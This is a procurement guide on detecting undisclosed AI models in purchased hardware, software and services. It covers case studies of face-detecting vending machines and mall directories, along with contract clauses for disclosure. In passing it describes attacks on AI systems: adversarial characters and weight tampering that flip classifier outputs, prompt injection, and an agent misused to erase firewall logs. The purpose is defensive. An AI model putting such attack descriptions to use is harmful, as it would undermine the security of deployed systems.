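# How buyers can detect undisclosed AI models in the hardware, software and services they purchase

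## What an undisclosed model is and where it can run

An AI model is a program whose behaviour depends on numbers learned in training instead of rules written by a programmer. Manufacturers build models into phones, cameras, industrial controllers and office software, and many online services send their customers' data to models that the customers never see. An *undisclosed model* is one that a product or service contains or relies on, and that nobody told the buyer about in terms a buyer would plausibly notice. The term covers models that the supplier doesn't know about as well as models that the supplier is hiding.

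A phone can contain many AI models that its buyer doesn't know about. In *Harvesting Apple's Orchard*, Agyemang, Asante and colleagues (2026) counted 320 model files on a single virtual iPhone running iOS 26.1. These models sort text messages, predict when the battery should finish charging, rank contacts and apps, and analyse every photo and video in the library. Apple advertises some of these features, but to list the models behind them, the researchers needed Apple's firmware images and jailbroken software, on which they had bypassed Apple's access restrictions.

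### Weights and inference engines

The learned numbers are the model's *weights*. A small model may have thousands of them and a large one has billions, usually stored in one or more files. *SoK* (Huang, Zheng and colleagues, 2026), a survey of AI security on phones, lists what else these files contain: the model's structure (the order of its calculations), the form of input it accepts, and extras such as the labels it can output.

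A weights file does nothing until an *inference engine* loads it. Inference engines are ordinary software, and common ones include LiteRT, ONNX Runtime and llama.cpp. Huang and colleagues give the example of an app that checks skin for cancer. The app turns the user's photo into a grid of numbers in the shape the model accepts. The engine loads the weights and performs the calculations the file specifies on the grid, possibly running some of them on a dedicated AI chip. It outputs another set of numbers, which the app converts into a prediction of melanoma and a referral to a dermatologist.

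A buyer has to look for both the weights and the engine, which may not arrive together. A product can ship with an engine and download the weights later, in which case an inspection on the day of delivery would find only the engine. Agyemang and colleagues describe three routes by which Apple's models reach a device: inside the operating system, in packages that Apple can vary independently of it, and as downloads on demand.

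### Classifiers, language models and agents

How much a buyer should worry about an undisclosed model depends heavily on what kind of model it is. CISA's *Principles for the Secure Integration of Artificial Intelligence in Operational Technology* (2025) defines machine-learning models, large language models and AI agents separately. CISA, the US cybersecurity agency, wrote it with partners in six other countries for operators of power stations, waterworks and similar plants, but roughly the same split works for purchases in general.

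A *narrow classifier* answers one kind of question about one kind of input, such as whether an email is spam, whether an image contains a face, or whether a bearing is failing. CISA notes that some modern programmable logic controllers, the small computers that control a pump or a production line, run lightweight models of this type to spot anomalies or balance loads. A factory that buys a controller can therefore also be buying a classifier without knowing it. Models that predict a quantity, such as the load on a power grid, raise the same questions for a buyer.

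A buyer should first find out what data a classifier takes in. A door camera that detects faces extracts information about passers-by that a plain door camera does not, even if no picture leaves the building. Classifiers also fail in ways that ordinary software testing would not look for. When Agyemang and colleagues inserted invisible characters into 20 test messages, one of Apple's text-message filters classified 13 of them differently. Altering 16 bytes in another model's weights file flipped its prediction for seven of eight test inputs, although that attack required a jailbroken device.

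A *general language model* accepts almost any text and responds in text, so a product's visible function is a poor guide to what the model could do with the data. For example, a help-desk tool that only drafts replies may contain a model that could also profile every customer who writes in. Image generators are similarly flexible.

The most pressing question is usually where the text goes. IPWatchdog's *From ‘Sneaky AI’ to ‘Ontology’* (2026) reports on a conference session where Curcio, a speaker from the vendors' side, distinguished "closed pool" systems, which keep customers' inputs contained, from "open pool" systems, whose vendors may train on them. Customers do not always realise which kind they are using.

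The developer's identity can also matter. Some governments and companies ban particular developers' models, and a product can contain a banned model under a different brand name. One reason CISA gives for caution about foreign suppliers generally is that they may have to obey directions from their own governments that conflict with the customer's interests. An undisclosed language model also adds a security risk, because an attacker can plant instructions in text the model will read, a technique called prompt injection.

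An *agent* is a model run in a loop with tools, so it can act without a person approving each action. In May 2026, ASD's ACSC, the Australian government's cyber security centre, and five partner agencies issued guidance that lists an agent's parts as incoming information, a goal, a model to choose the next step, access to tools, and privileges to act.

One of their hypothetical scenarios shows why the privileges matter. An organisation gives an agent broad write access so that it can install software patches. A malicious insider outside the privileged IT group asks it to apply a patch and also clean up the firewall logs. The agent does both because its permissions allow it to, whereas a language model without tools could only have written a reply.

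A buyer can't tell from a model's weights whether it is part of an agent, because that depends on the surrounding software. The same file can be used in a chat window or in a program that calls the model repeatedly and acts on its output with an administrator's password. A buyer who finds a language model therefore still has to check what tools and permissions the software gives it. Most documented cases of undisclosed AI involve classifiers or ordinary language models rather than agents.

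### Where the model runs

A model of any kind runs either on the buyer's own equipment or on someone else's. Both arrangements have physical requirements that leave traces, even if the supplier doesn't mention the model.

A *local* model needs storage for its weights, memory to hold them while it runs, and computation. Language models need a lot of all three. *Less Is More* (2026), an account of building language models into a phone app, lists the sizes of several small ones. Gemma 3 1B, with about a billion weights, takes up 1,005 MB of storage and needs a phone with at least 4 GB of memory. Gemma 4 E2B takes up 2,583 MB and needs 8 GB, and the larger E4B takes up 3,650 MB and needs 12 GB. These models use roughly one byte of storage per weight.

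Classifiers can be far smaller. Agyemang and colleagues found 281 files of apparently raw, unencrypted weights across Apple's software, totaling about 390 MB. That is an average of about 1.4 MB each, smaller than many photos. A search for very large files would miss most of Apple's models, though it would quickly find any of the Gemma models.

A *remote* model needs a network connection and little else from the buyer. In the arrangement Huang and colleagues describe, the device gathers data, sends a request and displays the answer, while a server holds the weights and runs the model. A cheap sensor can therefore use a very large model. CISA warns that some industrial devices with built-in AI may need internet access to function, and advises operators to ask vendors where the models are located. Many products combine local and remote models. A smart speaker, for example, can detect its wake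 word with a local classifier and send the speech that follows to a server.

Buyers can check for undisclosed models by questioning the supplier and reading its documents, including any bill of materials. A software bill of materials (SBOM) is a machine-readable list of the components in a piece of software, which CISA's *2026 Minimum Elements for a Software Bill of Materials (SBOM)* (2026) likens to a list of ingredients. A component is any separately identifiable part, such as a library, a file or an outside service. An SBOM for AI, or AIBOM, also lists models, datasets and their origins. A G7 working group has adopted minimum requirements for AIBOMs, according to ANSSI's *Software bill of materials (SBOM) for artificial intelligence* (2026).

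The other checks are technical. *Static analysis* means examining files without running them. *Runtime observation* means running the product and recording its memory, processor use, power draw and network traffic. *Model fingerprinting* means using a model's answers or timing to identify which model it is.

| Check | Trace of a local model | Trace of a remote model |
|---|---|---|
| Supplier's answers, SBOM or AIBOM | An entry for the model or engine, if the supplier lists it | An entry for the outside service, if the supplier lists it |
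| Static analysis | Weights files, inference-engine code | Addresses and code for contacting an AI service |
| Runtime observation: memory, processor, power | A rise in load when the model runs | Little or nothing |
| Runtime observation: network traffic | At most, a download of weights or updates | Connections and the amount of data sent |
| Model fingerprinting | Patterns in the output, if the product returns any | The same |

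*LLMAID* (Liu, Zhuo and colleagues, 2025) shows that static analysis can detect both sorts of trace. The tool examined 3,819 Android apps and identified 1,366 as containing AI. The AI components in those apps included 644 model files, which point to local models, and 120 web requests, some to remote services such as OpenAI's. Most of the other components were code packages and their interfaces. The researchers had picked apps whose store descriptions strongly suggested AI, so the figures don't show how common undisclosed models are.

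The remote column of the table applies only when the product contacts the AI service directly. If the product instead contacts the supplier's server, which forwards the data to a model at a third company, the buyer's network shows traffic only to the supplier. Fingerprinting may still work if the model's output comes back to the buyer. Otherwise, the buyer depends on what the supplier is willing to disclose or must disclose under contract.

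### Grades of non-disclosure

The mildest case is a model that the supplier mentions only in a manual or on a support page. A buyer who asks about it will probably get the information. This can happen with what Curcio calls "embedded AI", which is built so deeply into a product that users may not realise they are dealing with it. Apple's background models are a near example. This case is probably the most common, though there are no firm numbers.

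The problem is worse when the manufacturer knows about the model but the reseller does not. A buyer who asks the reseller gets an honest but wrong answer, so the question has to reach the manufacturer. The face-detecting vending machines at the University of Waterloo in Canada are a well-documented case in which the manufacturer's knowledge did not reach the buyer.

Other models arrive after the sale. Curcio uses the term "sneaky AI" for AI that suddenly appears in a product that did not include it before. According to a May 2026 account on Wired-Gov, a workshop held by techUK, the British technology trade body, found that suppliers regularly switch on AI in products already under contract, sometimes without the buyer's knowledge. Buying for Victoria's *Navigating AI procurement*, the Australian state's guidance for its own purchasing staff, warns of the same practice. The workshop finding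 is practitioners' testimony and the Victorian passage is a warning, so neither establishes how often this happens. One named example is Google's Chrome browser, which downloaded the language model Gemini Nano onto users' computers.

The most extreme case is deliberate concealment, where the supplier's answers are worthless and only technical checks or outside investigators can help. *A hidden network of nudifying tools was found* (Priyadarshini, 2026) reports on an investigation that found hundreds of apps secretly running explicit image generators behind fronts such as pet photo editors and language tutors. The apps were openly AI products, so a "contains AI" label would have been accurate for all of them but useless to the user.

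A second case is so far only an allegation. Anthropic's *Detecting and countering misuse of AI* (2026) accuses two Chinese competitors, DeepSeek and Moonshot AI, of feeding their users' conversations into Anthropic's model Claude and training their own models on the responses. *China Probes DeepSeek, Moonshot AI Over Anthropic's Claims* (Dellinger, 2026) puts the alleged scale at more than 23 million user inputs from Moonshot between May and July, and 12.1 million from DeepSeek in 14 days of July, some containing names, email addresses and company data. China's internet regulator was reportedly investigating both firms in September 2026. Anthropic has a commercial interest in the accusation. If the accusation is accurate, users knew they were talking to one model but could not see that Claude was also involved, because the data would have passed between servers.

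Neither case involves an agent. In the Cline incident, an attacker's tampered release of a coding tool did install an agent on developers' computers, but the tool was software and its maker was also a victim. A limited search of public reports up to December 2026 found no documented case of a supplier deliberately concealing an agent in a device it sold. This is weak evidence that none exists, because an agent whose model runs on a remote server can leave little on the device beyond a small program and some network traffic.

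## How a university bought face-detecting vending machines without knowing it

In 2023 the University of Waterloo in Ontario, Canada, signed a contract for snack vending and got 29 machines with small cameras and software that estimated people's age and gender. The university says it did not know about the software until one of the machines malfunctioned. The fullest account is *Privacy Complaint PX24-00001* (2025), a report by the Information and Privacy Commissioner of Ontario. The investigator, John Gayle, had the tender, the winning bid, the contract and the technical manuals, so the report shows what the university could have learned at each stage.

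The machines used a narrow AI classifier, not an agent, to detect faces and people in video and to estimate two attributes of each face.

| Date | Event |
|---|---|
| June 2023 | The university posts its tender for snack vending |
| October 2023 | It signs a contract with Adaria Vending Services |
| December 2023 | Adaria installs 29 machines on campus |
| February 2024 | A student photographs an error message, and the university has the face detection disabled |
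| March 2024 | The last machines leave campus |
| June 2025 | The regulator publishes its first report, which names the wrong software company |
| 27 August 2025 | The regulator issues the revised report |

### An error message

Lucas Di Pietro, an engineering student, discovered the software by accident when he saw a vending machine in the Modern Languages building displaying an error from a program called "Invenda.Vending.FacialRecognition.App". He posted a photo on Reddit. According to the University of Waterloo, a second student then found the camera by shining a phone flashlight at likely pinholes, and taped over the hole to test whether the machine still detected people approaching. A third looked up the manufacturer's sales brochures. River Stanley, who investigated the machines for the student publication mathNEWS, said in CTV News' *'Facial recognition' error message on vending machine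 sparks concern* that nobody would have known without the error.

The discovery depended on luck, because a program had to crash with its name on a public screen and the name had to be revealing. The program was an Invenda component that turned the face detector's results into statistics, not the detector itself. With a blander name, it might have attracted no attention.

### Four companies deep

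The university dealt only with Adaria, which stocked and maintained the machines. Adaria had bought or leased them from Mars, the confectionery company. Mars had hired Invenda, a Swiss software company, to manufacture and supply them. Invenda had installed another company's audience-measurement tool without customising it. The tool relied on a third-party software library to make its estimates.

The university had no contract with Mars or Invenda, and it told the regulator that Adaria had no contract with Invenda for these machines. To ask Invenda about the software it had installed, the university would therefore have had to go through Adaria and then Mars.

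Even after the scandal, the university gave the regulator the wrong name for the software's supplier, and the regulator published it in its first report. Torkin Manes' *Snacking into the Future*, a law firm's summary of that report, names the company as Quividi and says the software also recorded people's mood and whether they had beards or glasses. After the report came out, the company told the regulator that its software was not in the machines. The university confirmed this and supplied another name, and Gayle's revised report refers to the real supplier only as a third party.

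The revised report kept the same legal findings but changed its description of the data, which no longer mentions estimates of mood. Gayle took the mix-up as further evidence that the university had not understood what it was buying.

### What happened to each video frame

The camera streamed video continuously at either 1280 by 720 or 640 by 480 pixels. An object detector, a model trained to find faces and people, processed each frame. Two processes then ran at the same time.

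One model estimated age and gender. When the detector found a face, the software captured the image, extracted the facial features and compared them with "hundreds of thousands of faces" in its library. This description, from the manuals, may loosely refer to a model trained on that many faces, since an age estimator doesn't normally need to look faces up one by one. The software didn't save the image or the features to disk, and it repeated the process with the next frame.

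The other process counted people. It compared the people in the current frame with those in the previous one and added to the count anyone who had no match.

When someone bought a snack, the machine sent Invenda's cloud service the time, an estimated age and gender, and the number of people present. The university said the machine also recorded the item sold and where customers touched the screen. The software produced an estimate for at most 80% of sales. Separate software handled payments, and the university said nobody could match the payment records to the other data. Gayle found no evidence that any of the companies kept or reused the face images.

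Invenda Group (2025) said in a press statement that the feature existed to measure audiences for digital advertising. Selling snacks did not require it.

### Where the purchase could have caught it

The university had at least eight chances to find the model before the crash, though some were much better than others.

1. **The risk assessment.** University rules call for an information risk assessment when a department makes a substantial change to how it processes personal information. The questionnaire asks about technology with privacy risks, and gives biometrics and surveillance capabilities as examples. The Procurement and Food Services departments skipped it because they expected the machines to collect only payment data. This is circular: staff used their beliefs about the product to decide against the check that would have tested those beliefs. The regulator's guidance recommends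 writing down the reasons for such a decision, but Gayle received no record of any.

2. **The tender.** The university asked bidders for a picture and specifications of each machine, an outline of its technologies, and its data or network requirements. It also wanted diagrams showing where personal information would flow. A complete answer would have included the camera. Adaria's bid instead described its own device for reporting sales and stock, and did not explicitly mention face detection. The university had not required bidders to carry out a security assessment of the machines' technology.

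3. **The brochure.** Adaria wrote that it was working with Mars to test "product innovations" and would install new "Intelligent" machines. The attached brochure listed "High Traffic/Dwell Time" as a requirement. Gayle counted all this as a warning. The traffic half of the phrase is weak evidence, because any vending machine does better where more people pass. "Dwell time", meaning how long people linger, is a more suggestive term, since advertisers use it when they measure audiences.

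4. **The statement about subcontractors.** The tender asked for the role of every subcontractor, and Adaria replied that it would use none. The same bid described Mars's part in deploying the machines. Adaria may have seen no contradiction, because a company that supplies equipment is not obviously a subcontractor for the vending service. The university needed to ask who made the machine and who wrote its software.

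5. **The manufacturer's advertising.** Invenda did not hide the feature from potential customers. Techdirt's *Error Message Exposes Vending Machine’s Use Of Facial Recognition Tech* quotes the mathNEWS article, which reported that Invenda's sales brochures advertised estimates of age and gender. That article appeared about a week after the Reddit post, according to The Globe and Mail. But the students had Invenda's name from the error message. The university told the regulator that it had not known of Invenda's involvement, as the student newspaper reported in Imprint's *Information watchdog addresses UW responsibility in vending machine privacy violations* (2025).

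6. **The reseller.** Gayle concluded that Adaria, too, was apparently unaware that the machines collected face data. The evidence is a certificate in which an Adaria director stated that the company held no biometric information from them. This is thin, because a company can hold no such data and still know about the camera. Gayle thought that a privacy assessment by Adaria during the tender would probably have uncovered both Invenda and the face-detection supplier.

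7. **The audit right.** The contract allowed the university to hire an outside specialist to audit information security. Gayle describes no such audit before the malfunction. The contract also required Adaria and any subcontractors to obey Ontario's privacy law, and gave the university ownership of any personal information that Adaria created. Gayle considered these terms adequate on paper. They didn't help because nobody at the university knew there was face data to protect. The Information and Privacy Commissioner of Ontario warns in its general guidance on outsourcing that "contracts alone are not enough".

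8. **The machines themselves.** They stood on campus for about two months before the error appeared. A student found the camera with a phone and some tape, and the device tests described later in this report could have pointed to the software behind it.

Gayle puts most weight on the skipped risk assessment and says it would likely have exposed the warning signs. That may overestimate the questionnaire, because staff who didn't know about the camera could have answered "no" to the question about surveillance. The assessment would have worked only if it had prompted someone to ask how the "intelligent" machines operated, and to keep asking until they got an answer from Invenda. Examining a machine on delivery would not have depended on any supplier's knowledge or honesty.

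### The university's defence

The university disputed the regulator's conclusions and also its authority, arguing that federal privacy law applied because selling snacks is a commercial activity. Gayle replied that Ontario's law still covers personal information collected on a public university's behalf, even if federal law also applies to the vendor. The university's other arguments concerned the technology and the contract.

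The university called the camera an "optical sensor" and said, without giving evidence, that its resolution was too low to produce an identifiable image. Gayle cited forensic research that puts the bare minimum for identifying an unknown face at 20 pixels across the face, and noted that these cameras produced frames at least 640 pixels wide. A face fills only part of a frame, but 20 pixels is about 3% of that width, and the face of someone standing at a vending machine would normally take up more. The manuals also included a sample input image of photographic quality.

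A second argument was that the software held each image for only a few milliseconds. Ontario's law usually defines personal information as *recorded* information, but its rules on collection also cover unrecorded information. Gayle therefore needed to show only that the machine had captured the faces. The people counter also needed more than one frame in memory at once, which weakened the claim that the system worked entirely in real time.

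Third, the university argued that Adaria was not acting as its service provider when the machines collected face data, because it had hired Adaria to sell snacks and had never asked for the data. Gayle answered that a public body remains responsible for personal information that vendors collect on its behalf. Because the university had not known about the collection, the question became whether its purchasing process should have prevented it.

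Gayle found that the university had breached the law. Ontario's public bodies may collect personal information when a statute expressly authorises it, when it is used for law enforcement, or when it is necessary for a lawful activity. The machines could sell snacks without face images, even though the images might have been useful for understanding customers. The university had also given no notice of the collection.

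The suppliers' assurances did not change the result, and Mars's was wrong. Mars wrote that the machines could not "capture, retain or transmit imagery", but Invenda's letter about the same machines described software that processed digital images from a USB sensor. If the university had asked Mars in 2023, it might have received the same false assurance.

Some lawyers were uneasy about the decision. The Canadian Technology Law Association's *Always look under the hood* (2025) observed that the regulator had faulted a university for technology that it did not know about and "arguably would not have expected". The objection is fair, because few people buying a snack service would think to ask about face detection, and the clues in Adaria's bid are much easier to spot once you know the machines had it.

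But the university could have asked what was new about the machines without suspecting that they detected faces, because its supplier had told it they were new, "intelligent" and part of a test of innovations. A buyer can easily ask the maker of any "smart" product the same question. The university accepted Gayle's recommendation to assess such purchases in future, and since July 2025, Ontario law has required a privacy assessment in similar circumstances.

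### The Cadillac Fairview mall directories

An earlier Canadian case shows that a buyer can know about one model in a product and still miss another. In 2018 Cadillac Fairview, a large owner of shopping malls, tested face-analysis software in the touch-screen maps at 12 malls to estimate the number, age and gender of visitors. This system was also a narrow classifier with no agent in it. It also came to light through a photo on Reddit, which showed a screen in a Calgary mall displaying the words "FaceEncoder" and "FaceAnalyzer".

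The Office of the Privacy Commissioner of Canada's *Joint investigation of the Cadillac Fairview Corporation Limited* (2020), conducted with the Alberta and British Columbia commissioners, examined the equipment directly. Cadillac Fairview's contract with its supplier, Mappedin, mentioned webcams but not the face software. Cadillac Fairview initially told investigators that the system used an open-source program called Rude Carnie to estimate age and gender and kept only anonymous results.

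The investigators discovered a second model, FaceNet, through records they extracted from a directory. FaceNet converts a picture of a face into a string of numbers, called an embedding, designed so that two pictures of the same person produce similar strings. Mappedin had kept 5,061,324 embeddings on a decommissioned server. It could not explain why, and said the programmer responsible had left. The commissioners found no evidence that anyone had used the embeddings to identify shoppers, but ruled that Cadillac Fairview had collected and used personal information without valid consent.

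The courts have been more sympathetic to Cadillac Fairview. In *Cleaver v. The Cadillac Fairview Corporation Limited* (2025), decided in May 2025, a judge of the Supreme Court of British Columbia refused to let shoppers sue as a class. She accepted the commissioners' report as background but not as proof that its contents were true. The main technical evidence came from Richard Zhang, a computer scientist testifying for the company. Zhang ran 35 photos of the two plaintiffs through the software and searched the stored data for the closest embeddings. For one plaintiff, who had visited a Vancouver mall, the 15 closest all came from other provinces. For the other, the closest dated from after that plaintiff's visit.

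The experiment is decent evidence that the stored numbers were a poor way to find a particular person, although it tested only two people. It has no bearing on whether the cameras captured faces.

The province's Court of Appeal upheld the refusal in August 2026. It agreed that the plaintiffs had shown no factual basis for their claim that the company recorded facial images or biometric information (Bennett Jones, *BC Court Of Appeal*, 2026). The judges also saw no apparent damage to shoppers (Mach, *BCCA*, 2026).

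Invenda Group cited the 2025 decision in its defence over the Waterloo machines, but Gayle was not persuaded by it. The decision concerned whether a class action could go ahead, and the court never ruled on whether holding a face in memory for a moment counts as collecting it. Under the Ontario provision that applied to Waterloo, holding a face even that briefly is collection. A buyer with an undisclosed face detector can therefore breach privacy law even if the people it scanned would struggle to win damages.

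## What to ask suppliers and put in the contract

Asking the supplier is the easiest way to look for an undisclosed model, and sometimes the only way. If a supplier forwards its customers' data to another company's model, the customers may have nothing they can test. However, "Does the product use AI?" is a bad question to ask, even though it is the obvious one.

### Why the obvious question fails

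People disagree about what AI is. An engineer may think of a face counter as ordinary image processing, and the University of Waterloo called its vending machines' cameras "optical sensors". Official definitions also leave a lot out. *Driving Efficient Acquisition of Artificial Intelligence in Government* (Vought, 2025), which is memorandum M-25-22 from the Office of Management and Budget (OMB), sets out the US government's main rules for buying AI. It uses a statutory definition of "AI system" that excludes "any common commercial product within which artificial intelligence is embedded". Its example is a word processor that suggests text and corrects grammar, so a supplier using this definition could truthfully say that such a product is not an AI system.

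The word "use" is also ambiguous. A model may be present but switched off until a later update. It may run on a server, and the supplier may then feel entitled to say the product itself contains no AI. Some suppliers will think the buyer is asking whether their staff wrote the bid with a chatbot.

The person answering the buyer's questions may not know which AI models a product uses, and a reseller may know even less than the vendor. Foley & Lardner's *AI Bills of Materials (AI-BOMs) and Model Provenance*, a law firm's advice to manufacturers, warns that a standard vendor questionnaire may describe the vendor's security programme without revealing the open-source model or outside service inside the product.

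### Six better questions

A supplier can't answer all of these questions truthfully without disclosing every model it knows about. The questions refer to trained models instead of "AI".

1. *Does any component, whoever made it, run a trained model or send data to one?* The supplier should include components that are switched off and anything the product downloads after installation. "Whoever made it" is there because the model may belong to a supplier's supplier, as it did at Waterloo.

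2. *Which model is it, which version, and who developed it?* A brand name is not enough, since "our own assistant" may be another company's language model under a new label. If the supplier has trained an existing model further, the buyer needs the name of the original too.

3. *Where does the model run, and who receives the data?* "In the cloud" doesn't answer this. The supplier should name each company whose servers receive the customer's data and state whether any of them trains models on it.

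4. *What can the model do without a person's approval?* This question is meant to catch agents. A good answer lists the tools, accounts and permissions that the software gives the model, such as the ability to send email, delete files or run commands.

5. *Can the customer switch it off, and what stops working?* The supplier should explain whether "off" stops the model or merely hides its button, and whether the setting survives an update.

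6. *What can change through an update, and who decides?* A supplier that calls another company's model over the network may not control when that company replaces it. It should be willing to admit this.

The buyer should also ask how the supplier knows whether the product contains an AI model. A useful reply names the person or company that provided the information and lists any components the supplier couldn't trace. "We don't know what is in the camera module" is much more useful than a confident "no" because it shows the buyer what to test.

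The first question can produce too much information. An iPhone contains hundreds of model files, and someone buying office phones has little use for a page on each. As a reasonable compromise, the supplier could list every model, with one line on what data it takes in and what it produces. The supplier would then answer the other five questions only for models that handle personal or confidential data, generate text or images, or take actions.

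If a supplier objects that the details are confidential, Foley & Lardner suggest that it could deposit the information with a third party, let an outside reviewer examine it, or disclose the sensitive parts under stricter confidentiality terms. A small customer of a large software company may get none of these, but it can still record the refusal and decide whether to buy.

### Making the answers binding

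Many contracts state that only the signed document counts, which can strip a sales questionnaire of its legal force. The buyer should therefore attach the answers to the contract and have the supplier warrant them, meaning promise that they are true. A *disclosure warranty* could read:

> The supplier warrants that Schedule A lists every trained model that the product contains, downloads or sends customer data to, including models made by others.

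If the supplier warrants the list and it is wrong, the supplier has broken the contract, and the buyer doesn't need to prove that anyone lied. Suppliers will often try to add "to the best of our knowledge", which greatly weakens the warranty because a reseller that never asked the manufacturer could give a wrong answer without breaching it. If the buyer must accept a qualification, "after written enquiry of the maker of each component" is better because it at least requires the supplier to ask.

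A warranty also describes the product on one date, so the supplier has to renew it when the product changes. Foley & Lardner recommend that vendors vouch that their AI records are "materially accurate and complete". A supplier could argue that a small classifier isn't material, so a buyer who cares about classifiers should delete the word "materially".

### Reaching the supplier's suppliers

A *flow-down clause* is a term that a supplier must also impose on its own suppliers. Because a reseller may not know what a product contains, the clause requires each company in the chain to tell its customer what it has installed. At Waterloo, this requirement would have had to pass through every company between Adaria and the makers of the face-detection software.

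Suppliers can't pass the clause on to a company with which they have no contract. A developer that publishes a model's weights for anyone to download may never learn who is using them. In comments on a draft federal clause, PSC (2026), an association of US government contractors, called flow-down duties for the developers of such models "unworkable". Pullin, Kramarczyk and Robbins (2026) made a related criticism of the same draft in *GSA Issues a Revised Proposed Clause Governing AI Data-Safeguarding Requirements*, saying that some AI providers have no contract with the government and may not know that they are supporting a federal project.

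These are good objections to requiring promises from a distant developer, but they are much weaker objections to requiring disclosure, because the company that downloaded the model knows it did and can tell the buyer even if the developer never signs anything.

A flow-down clause should name manufacturers, software suppliers and distributors, because a supplier may not consider them subcontractors. Adaria apparently did not count Mars as one. Even a well-drafted clause usually gives the buyer no direct claim against a company several tiers down. If Invenda had broken its promise to Mars, it would normally have been up to Mars to enforce it.

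### Notice before a model is added or replaced

An accurate answer can become false the next time the supplier updates its software. A notice clause makes the supplier warn the buyer first, and the best-documented examples come from the General Services Administration (GSA), which runs many of the US government's purchasing contracts. In March 2026 it proposed a contract clause, GSA's *Basic Safeguarding of Artificial Intelligence Systems* (2026), with several kinds of notice:

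| Event | Contractor's duty in the March 2026 draft |
|---|---|
| A planned material change to the AI systems it has disclosed | Written notice at least 30 days before |
| A new AI service provider, or a material change to an existing one | Written notice at least 30 days before |
| Replacement of a model in use | Reasonable effort to give access to the new model alongside the old one, for 30 days (major version) or 15 days (minor version) |
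| A change that materially increases bias, weakens safeguards or worsens performance | Notice within 7 days of identifying the change |

The last duty is much weaker than the first two for a buyer looking for undisclosed models. The seven days start when the contractor identifies the change, so the model may already be running. Notice is also required only if the contractor concludes that the change made something worse, which is unlikely when it has just installed a model it considers better. A private contract should tie notice to a plain fact, such as a new model file or a new company receiving data, to leave less to the supplier's judgement.

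Notice is more useful if the buyer can act on it. *AI Contracts Need a Model Evaluation Window* (Zava, 2026), a blog post on GSA's final clause, recommends that private buyers copy the clause's combination of notice, access to the successor model and tests run by the buyer, but adds that they shouldn't assume they have GSA's bargaining power. A buyer with less leverage might settle for the right to postpone an update or keep the new feature off. A notice clause won't help if the supplier doesn't hear about the change, which can happen when it rents a model from another company.

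### Audit and test rights

An audit right lets the buyer examine the supplier's records, and a test right lets it run or inspect the product. Vought's memorandum has unusually strict rules for testing. Federal agencies must run independent evaluations on data they have defined themselves, which the vendor should not have access to. Vendors must allow enough access and time for the evaluation. If an agency lets the vendor do the testing, it must ask for results detailed enough for someone else to verify or reproduce, where practicable.

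These rules are sensible for checking whether a known model works, but they would not necessarily reveal an unknown one. For example, asking a help-desk chatbot a thousand test questions would not show whether a separate classifier ranks the customers who use it. To look for undisclosed models, the buyer needs the right to a complete copy of the delivered software, a sample device to take apart, a list of the outside services the product contacts, and the supplier's record of the components in each version.

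Waterloo apparently never used its audit right before the scandal, so it is worth setting a date for the first inspection, ideally before final payment. The right also needs to extend beyond the reseller, because the reseller's records may be as incomplete as its answers. Confidentiality may again be an obstacle. Crowell & Moring's *GSA Issues Proposed AI Contract Clause, Seeks Feedback* (2026) notes that GSA's second draft, of June 2026, exempted trade secrets from the contractor's documentation duties. A supplier could try to use such an exemption to withhold a model's identity, and the contract should rule that out.

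### Permission to reverse engineer

Many software licences forbid customers to decompile the program, which means turning it back into code a person can read. Some also forbid them to publish test results. A buyer who unpacks an app to look for model weights could therefore break the licence while checking whether the supplier has complied with the contract.

The contract can solve this by giving the buyer permission to unpack, decompile and monitor the product to identify its components and check its security. It should also let the buyer hire a specialist and share the findings with regulators. The supplier can reasonably ask the buyer not to copy the product or extract the model for its own use.

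The EU's Software Directive already lets lawful users observe, study and test how a program works, whatever the licence says. Its right to decompile is narrower and mainly serves compatibility with other software. The law varies outside the EU.

A reseller can't give permission on behalf of a manufacturer that owns the code, so the buyer may need the manufacturer's signature. Permission also doesn't give the buyer a technical way into a locked device such as an iPhone.

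### Remedies for false statements

The final term sets out what happens if the list of models turns out to be wrong. Ordinary damages are a poor remedy because the buyer may struggle to show a financial loss from, for example, a camera that estimated people's ages. A better term requires the supplier to disable any undisclosed model at its own expense, delete the data it collected, pay for the investigation, and let the buyer end the contract with a refund.

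Suppliers will want limits on their liability. GSA's final clause lets the government suspend use of a language model at any time. But when the government ends a contract for cause, the clause caps the contractor's liability for decommissioning costs at 25% of the affected order, as Will (2026) reports in *GSA issued an AI acquisition policy for new contracts*. Such a cap could leave the buyer of an inexpensive device paying most of the cost of removing it from hundreds of rooms.

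Harsh penalties can also discourage disclosure. A supplier that discovers an unlisted model a month after signing has no reason to report it if the penalty is the same as for getting caught. The contract could allow a short period for correcting honest mistakes and reserve the heaviest penalties for suppliers that knew about the model or refused to ask. All of these remedies depend on someone finding the model.

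### What US federal buyers require

Vought's memorandum has applied to new federal solicitations since about the end of September 2025, and to renewals of older contracts. It doesn't cover national security systems. It also excludes common commercial products, so it mostly doesn't cover AI in products sold as something else. Agencies decide whether this exclusion applies by considering whether the product is widely available to the public and whether it has substantial purposes other than AI. A snack machine clearly has such a purpose, so one that detects faces would be exempt if an agency judged it widely available.

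Vought predicts in the memorandum that vendors will increasingly use AI in ways the government doesn't anticipate, and tells agencies to consider whether a solicitation should require disclosure. Agencies also "should consider" requiring notice of new AI features. Each agency decides whether to impose either requirement. Some of the testing rules described above are mandatory, but they apply to AI that the agency knows it is buying.

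GSA's March 2026 draft came closest to a general disclosure rule. It would have required contractors to "disclose all AI systems used in performance of this contract" within 30 days of award. But the draft took its definition of "AI system" from the same statute as Vought's memorandum, so it had the same exclusion for common commercial products. The deadline also fell after the award, when the buyer has already given up most of its leverage.

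The draft was broad in other respects, including a ban on foreign AI components, and contractors objected strongly. According to Pullin and colleagues, the June version covered only large language models that process government data. It expressly excluded models embedded in common commercial products and models incidental to the contract's main purpose.

The final clause took effect on 19 October 2026 as a "deviation", a change to purchasing rules that GSA can use before formal rulemaking. The law firm Wiley summarises it in *GSA Releases Final Language of AI Contract Clause* (2026). The clause applies when the government buys a language model, chatbot, agentic system, LLM-enabled office tool or something similar, provided that the language model is a "material feature" and government data goes into or comes out of it. The clause is removed from the contract if only the contractor's internal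 systems use the model.

This clause improves on the June draft by expressly including office software with a built-in language model. It still doesn't cover narrow classifiers, so it would not have applied to the Waterloo machines. A language model hidden deep in a product also might not count as a material feature. And a contractor who doesn't know that its product calls a language model can't know that the clause applies.

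Most of the checking relies on documents. According to Wiley, contractors show compliance through flow-down terms, subcontractors' attestations and records of their own due diligence. They must use best efforts when vetting subcontractors and must report material violations within 72 hours. The government can also run automated tests of the language model for bias, truthfulness and safety, but again only if it knows the model is there.

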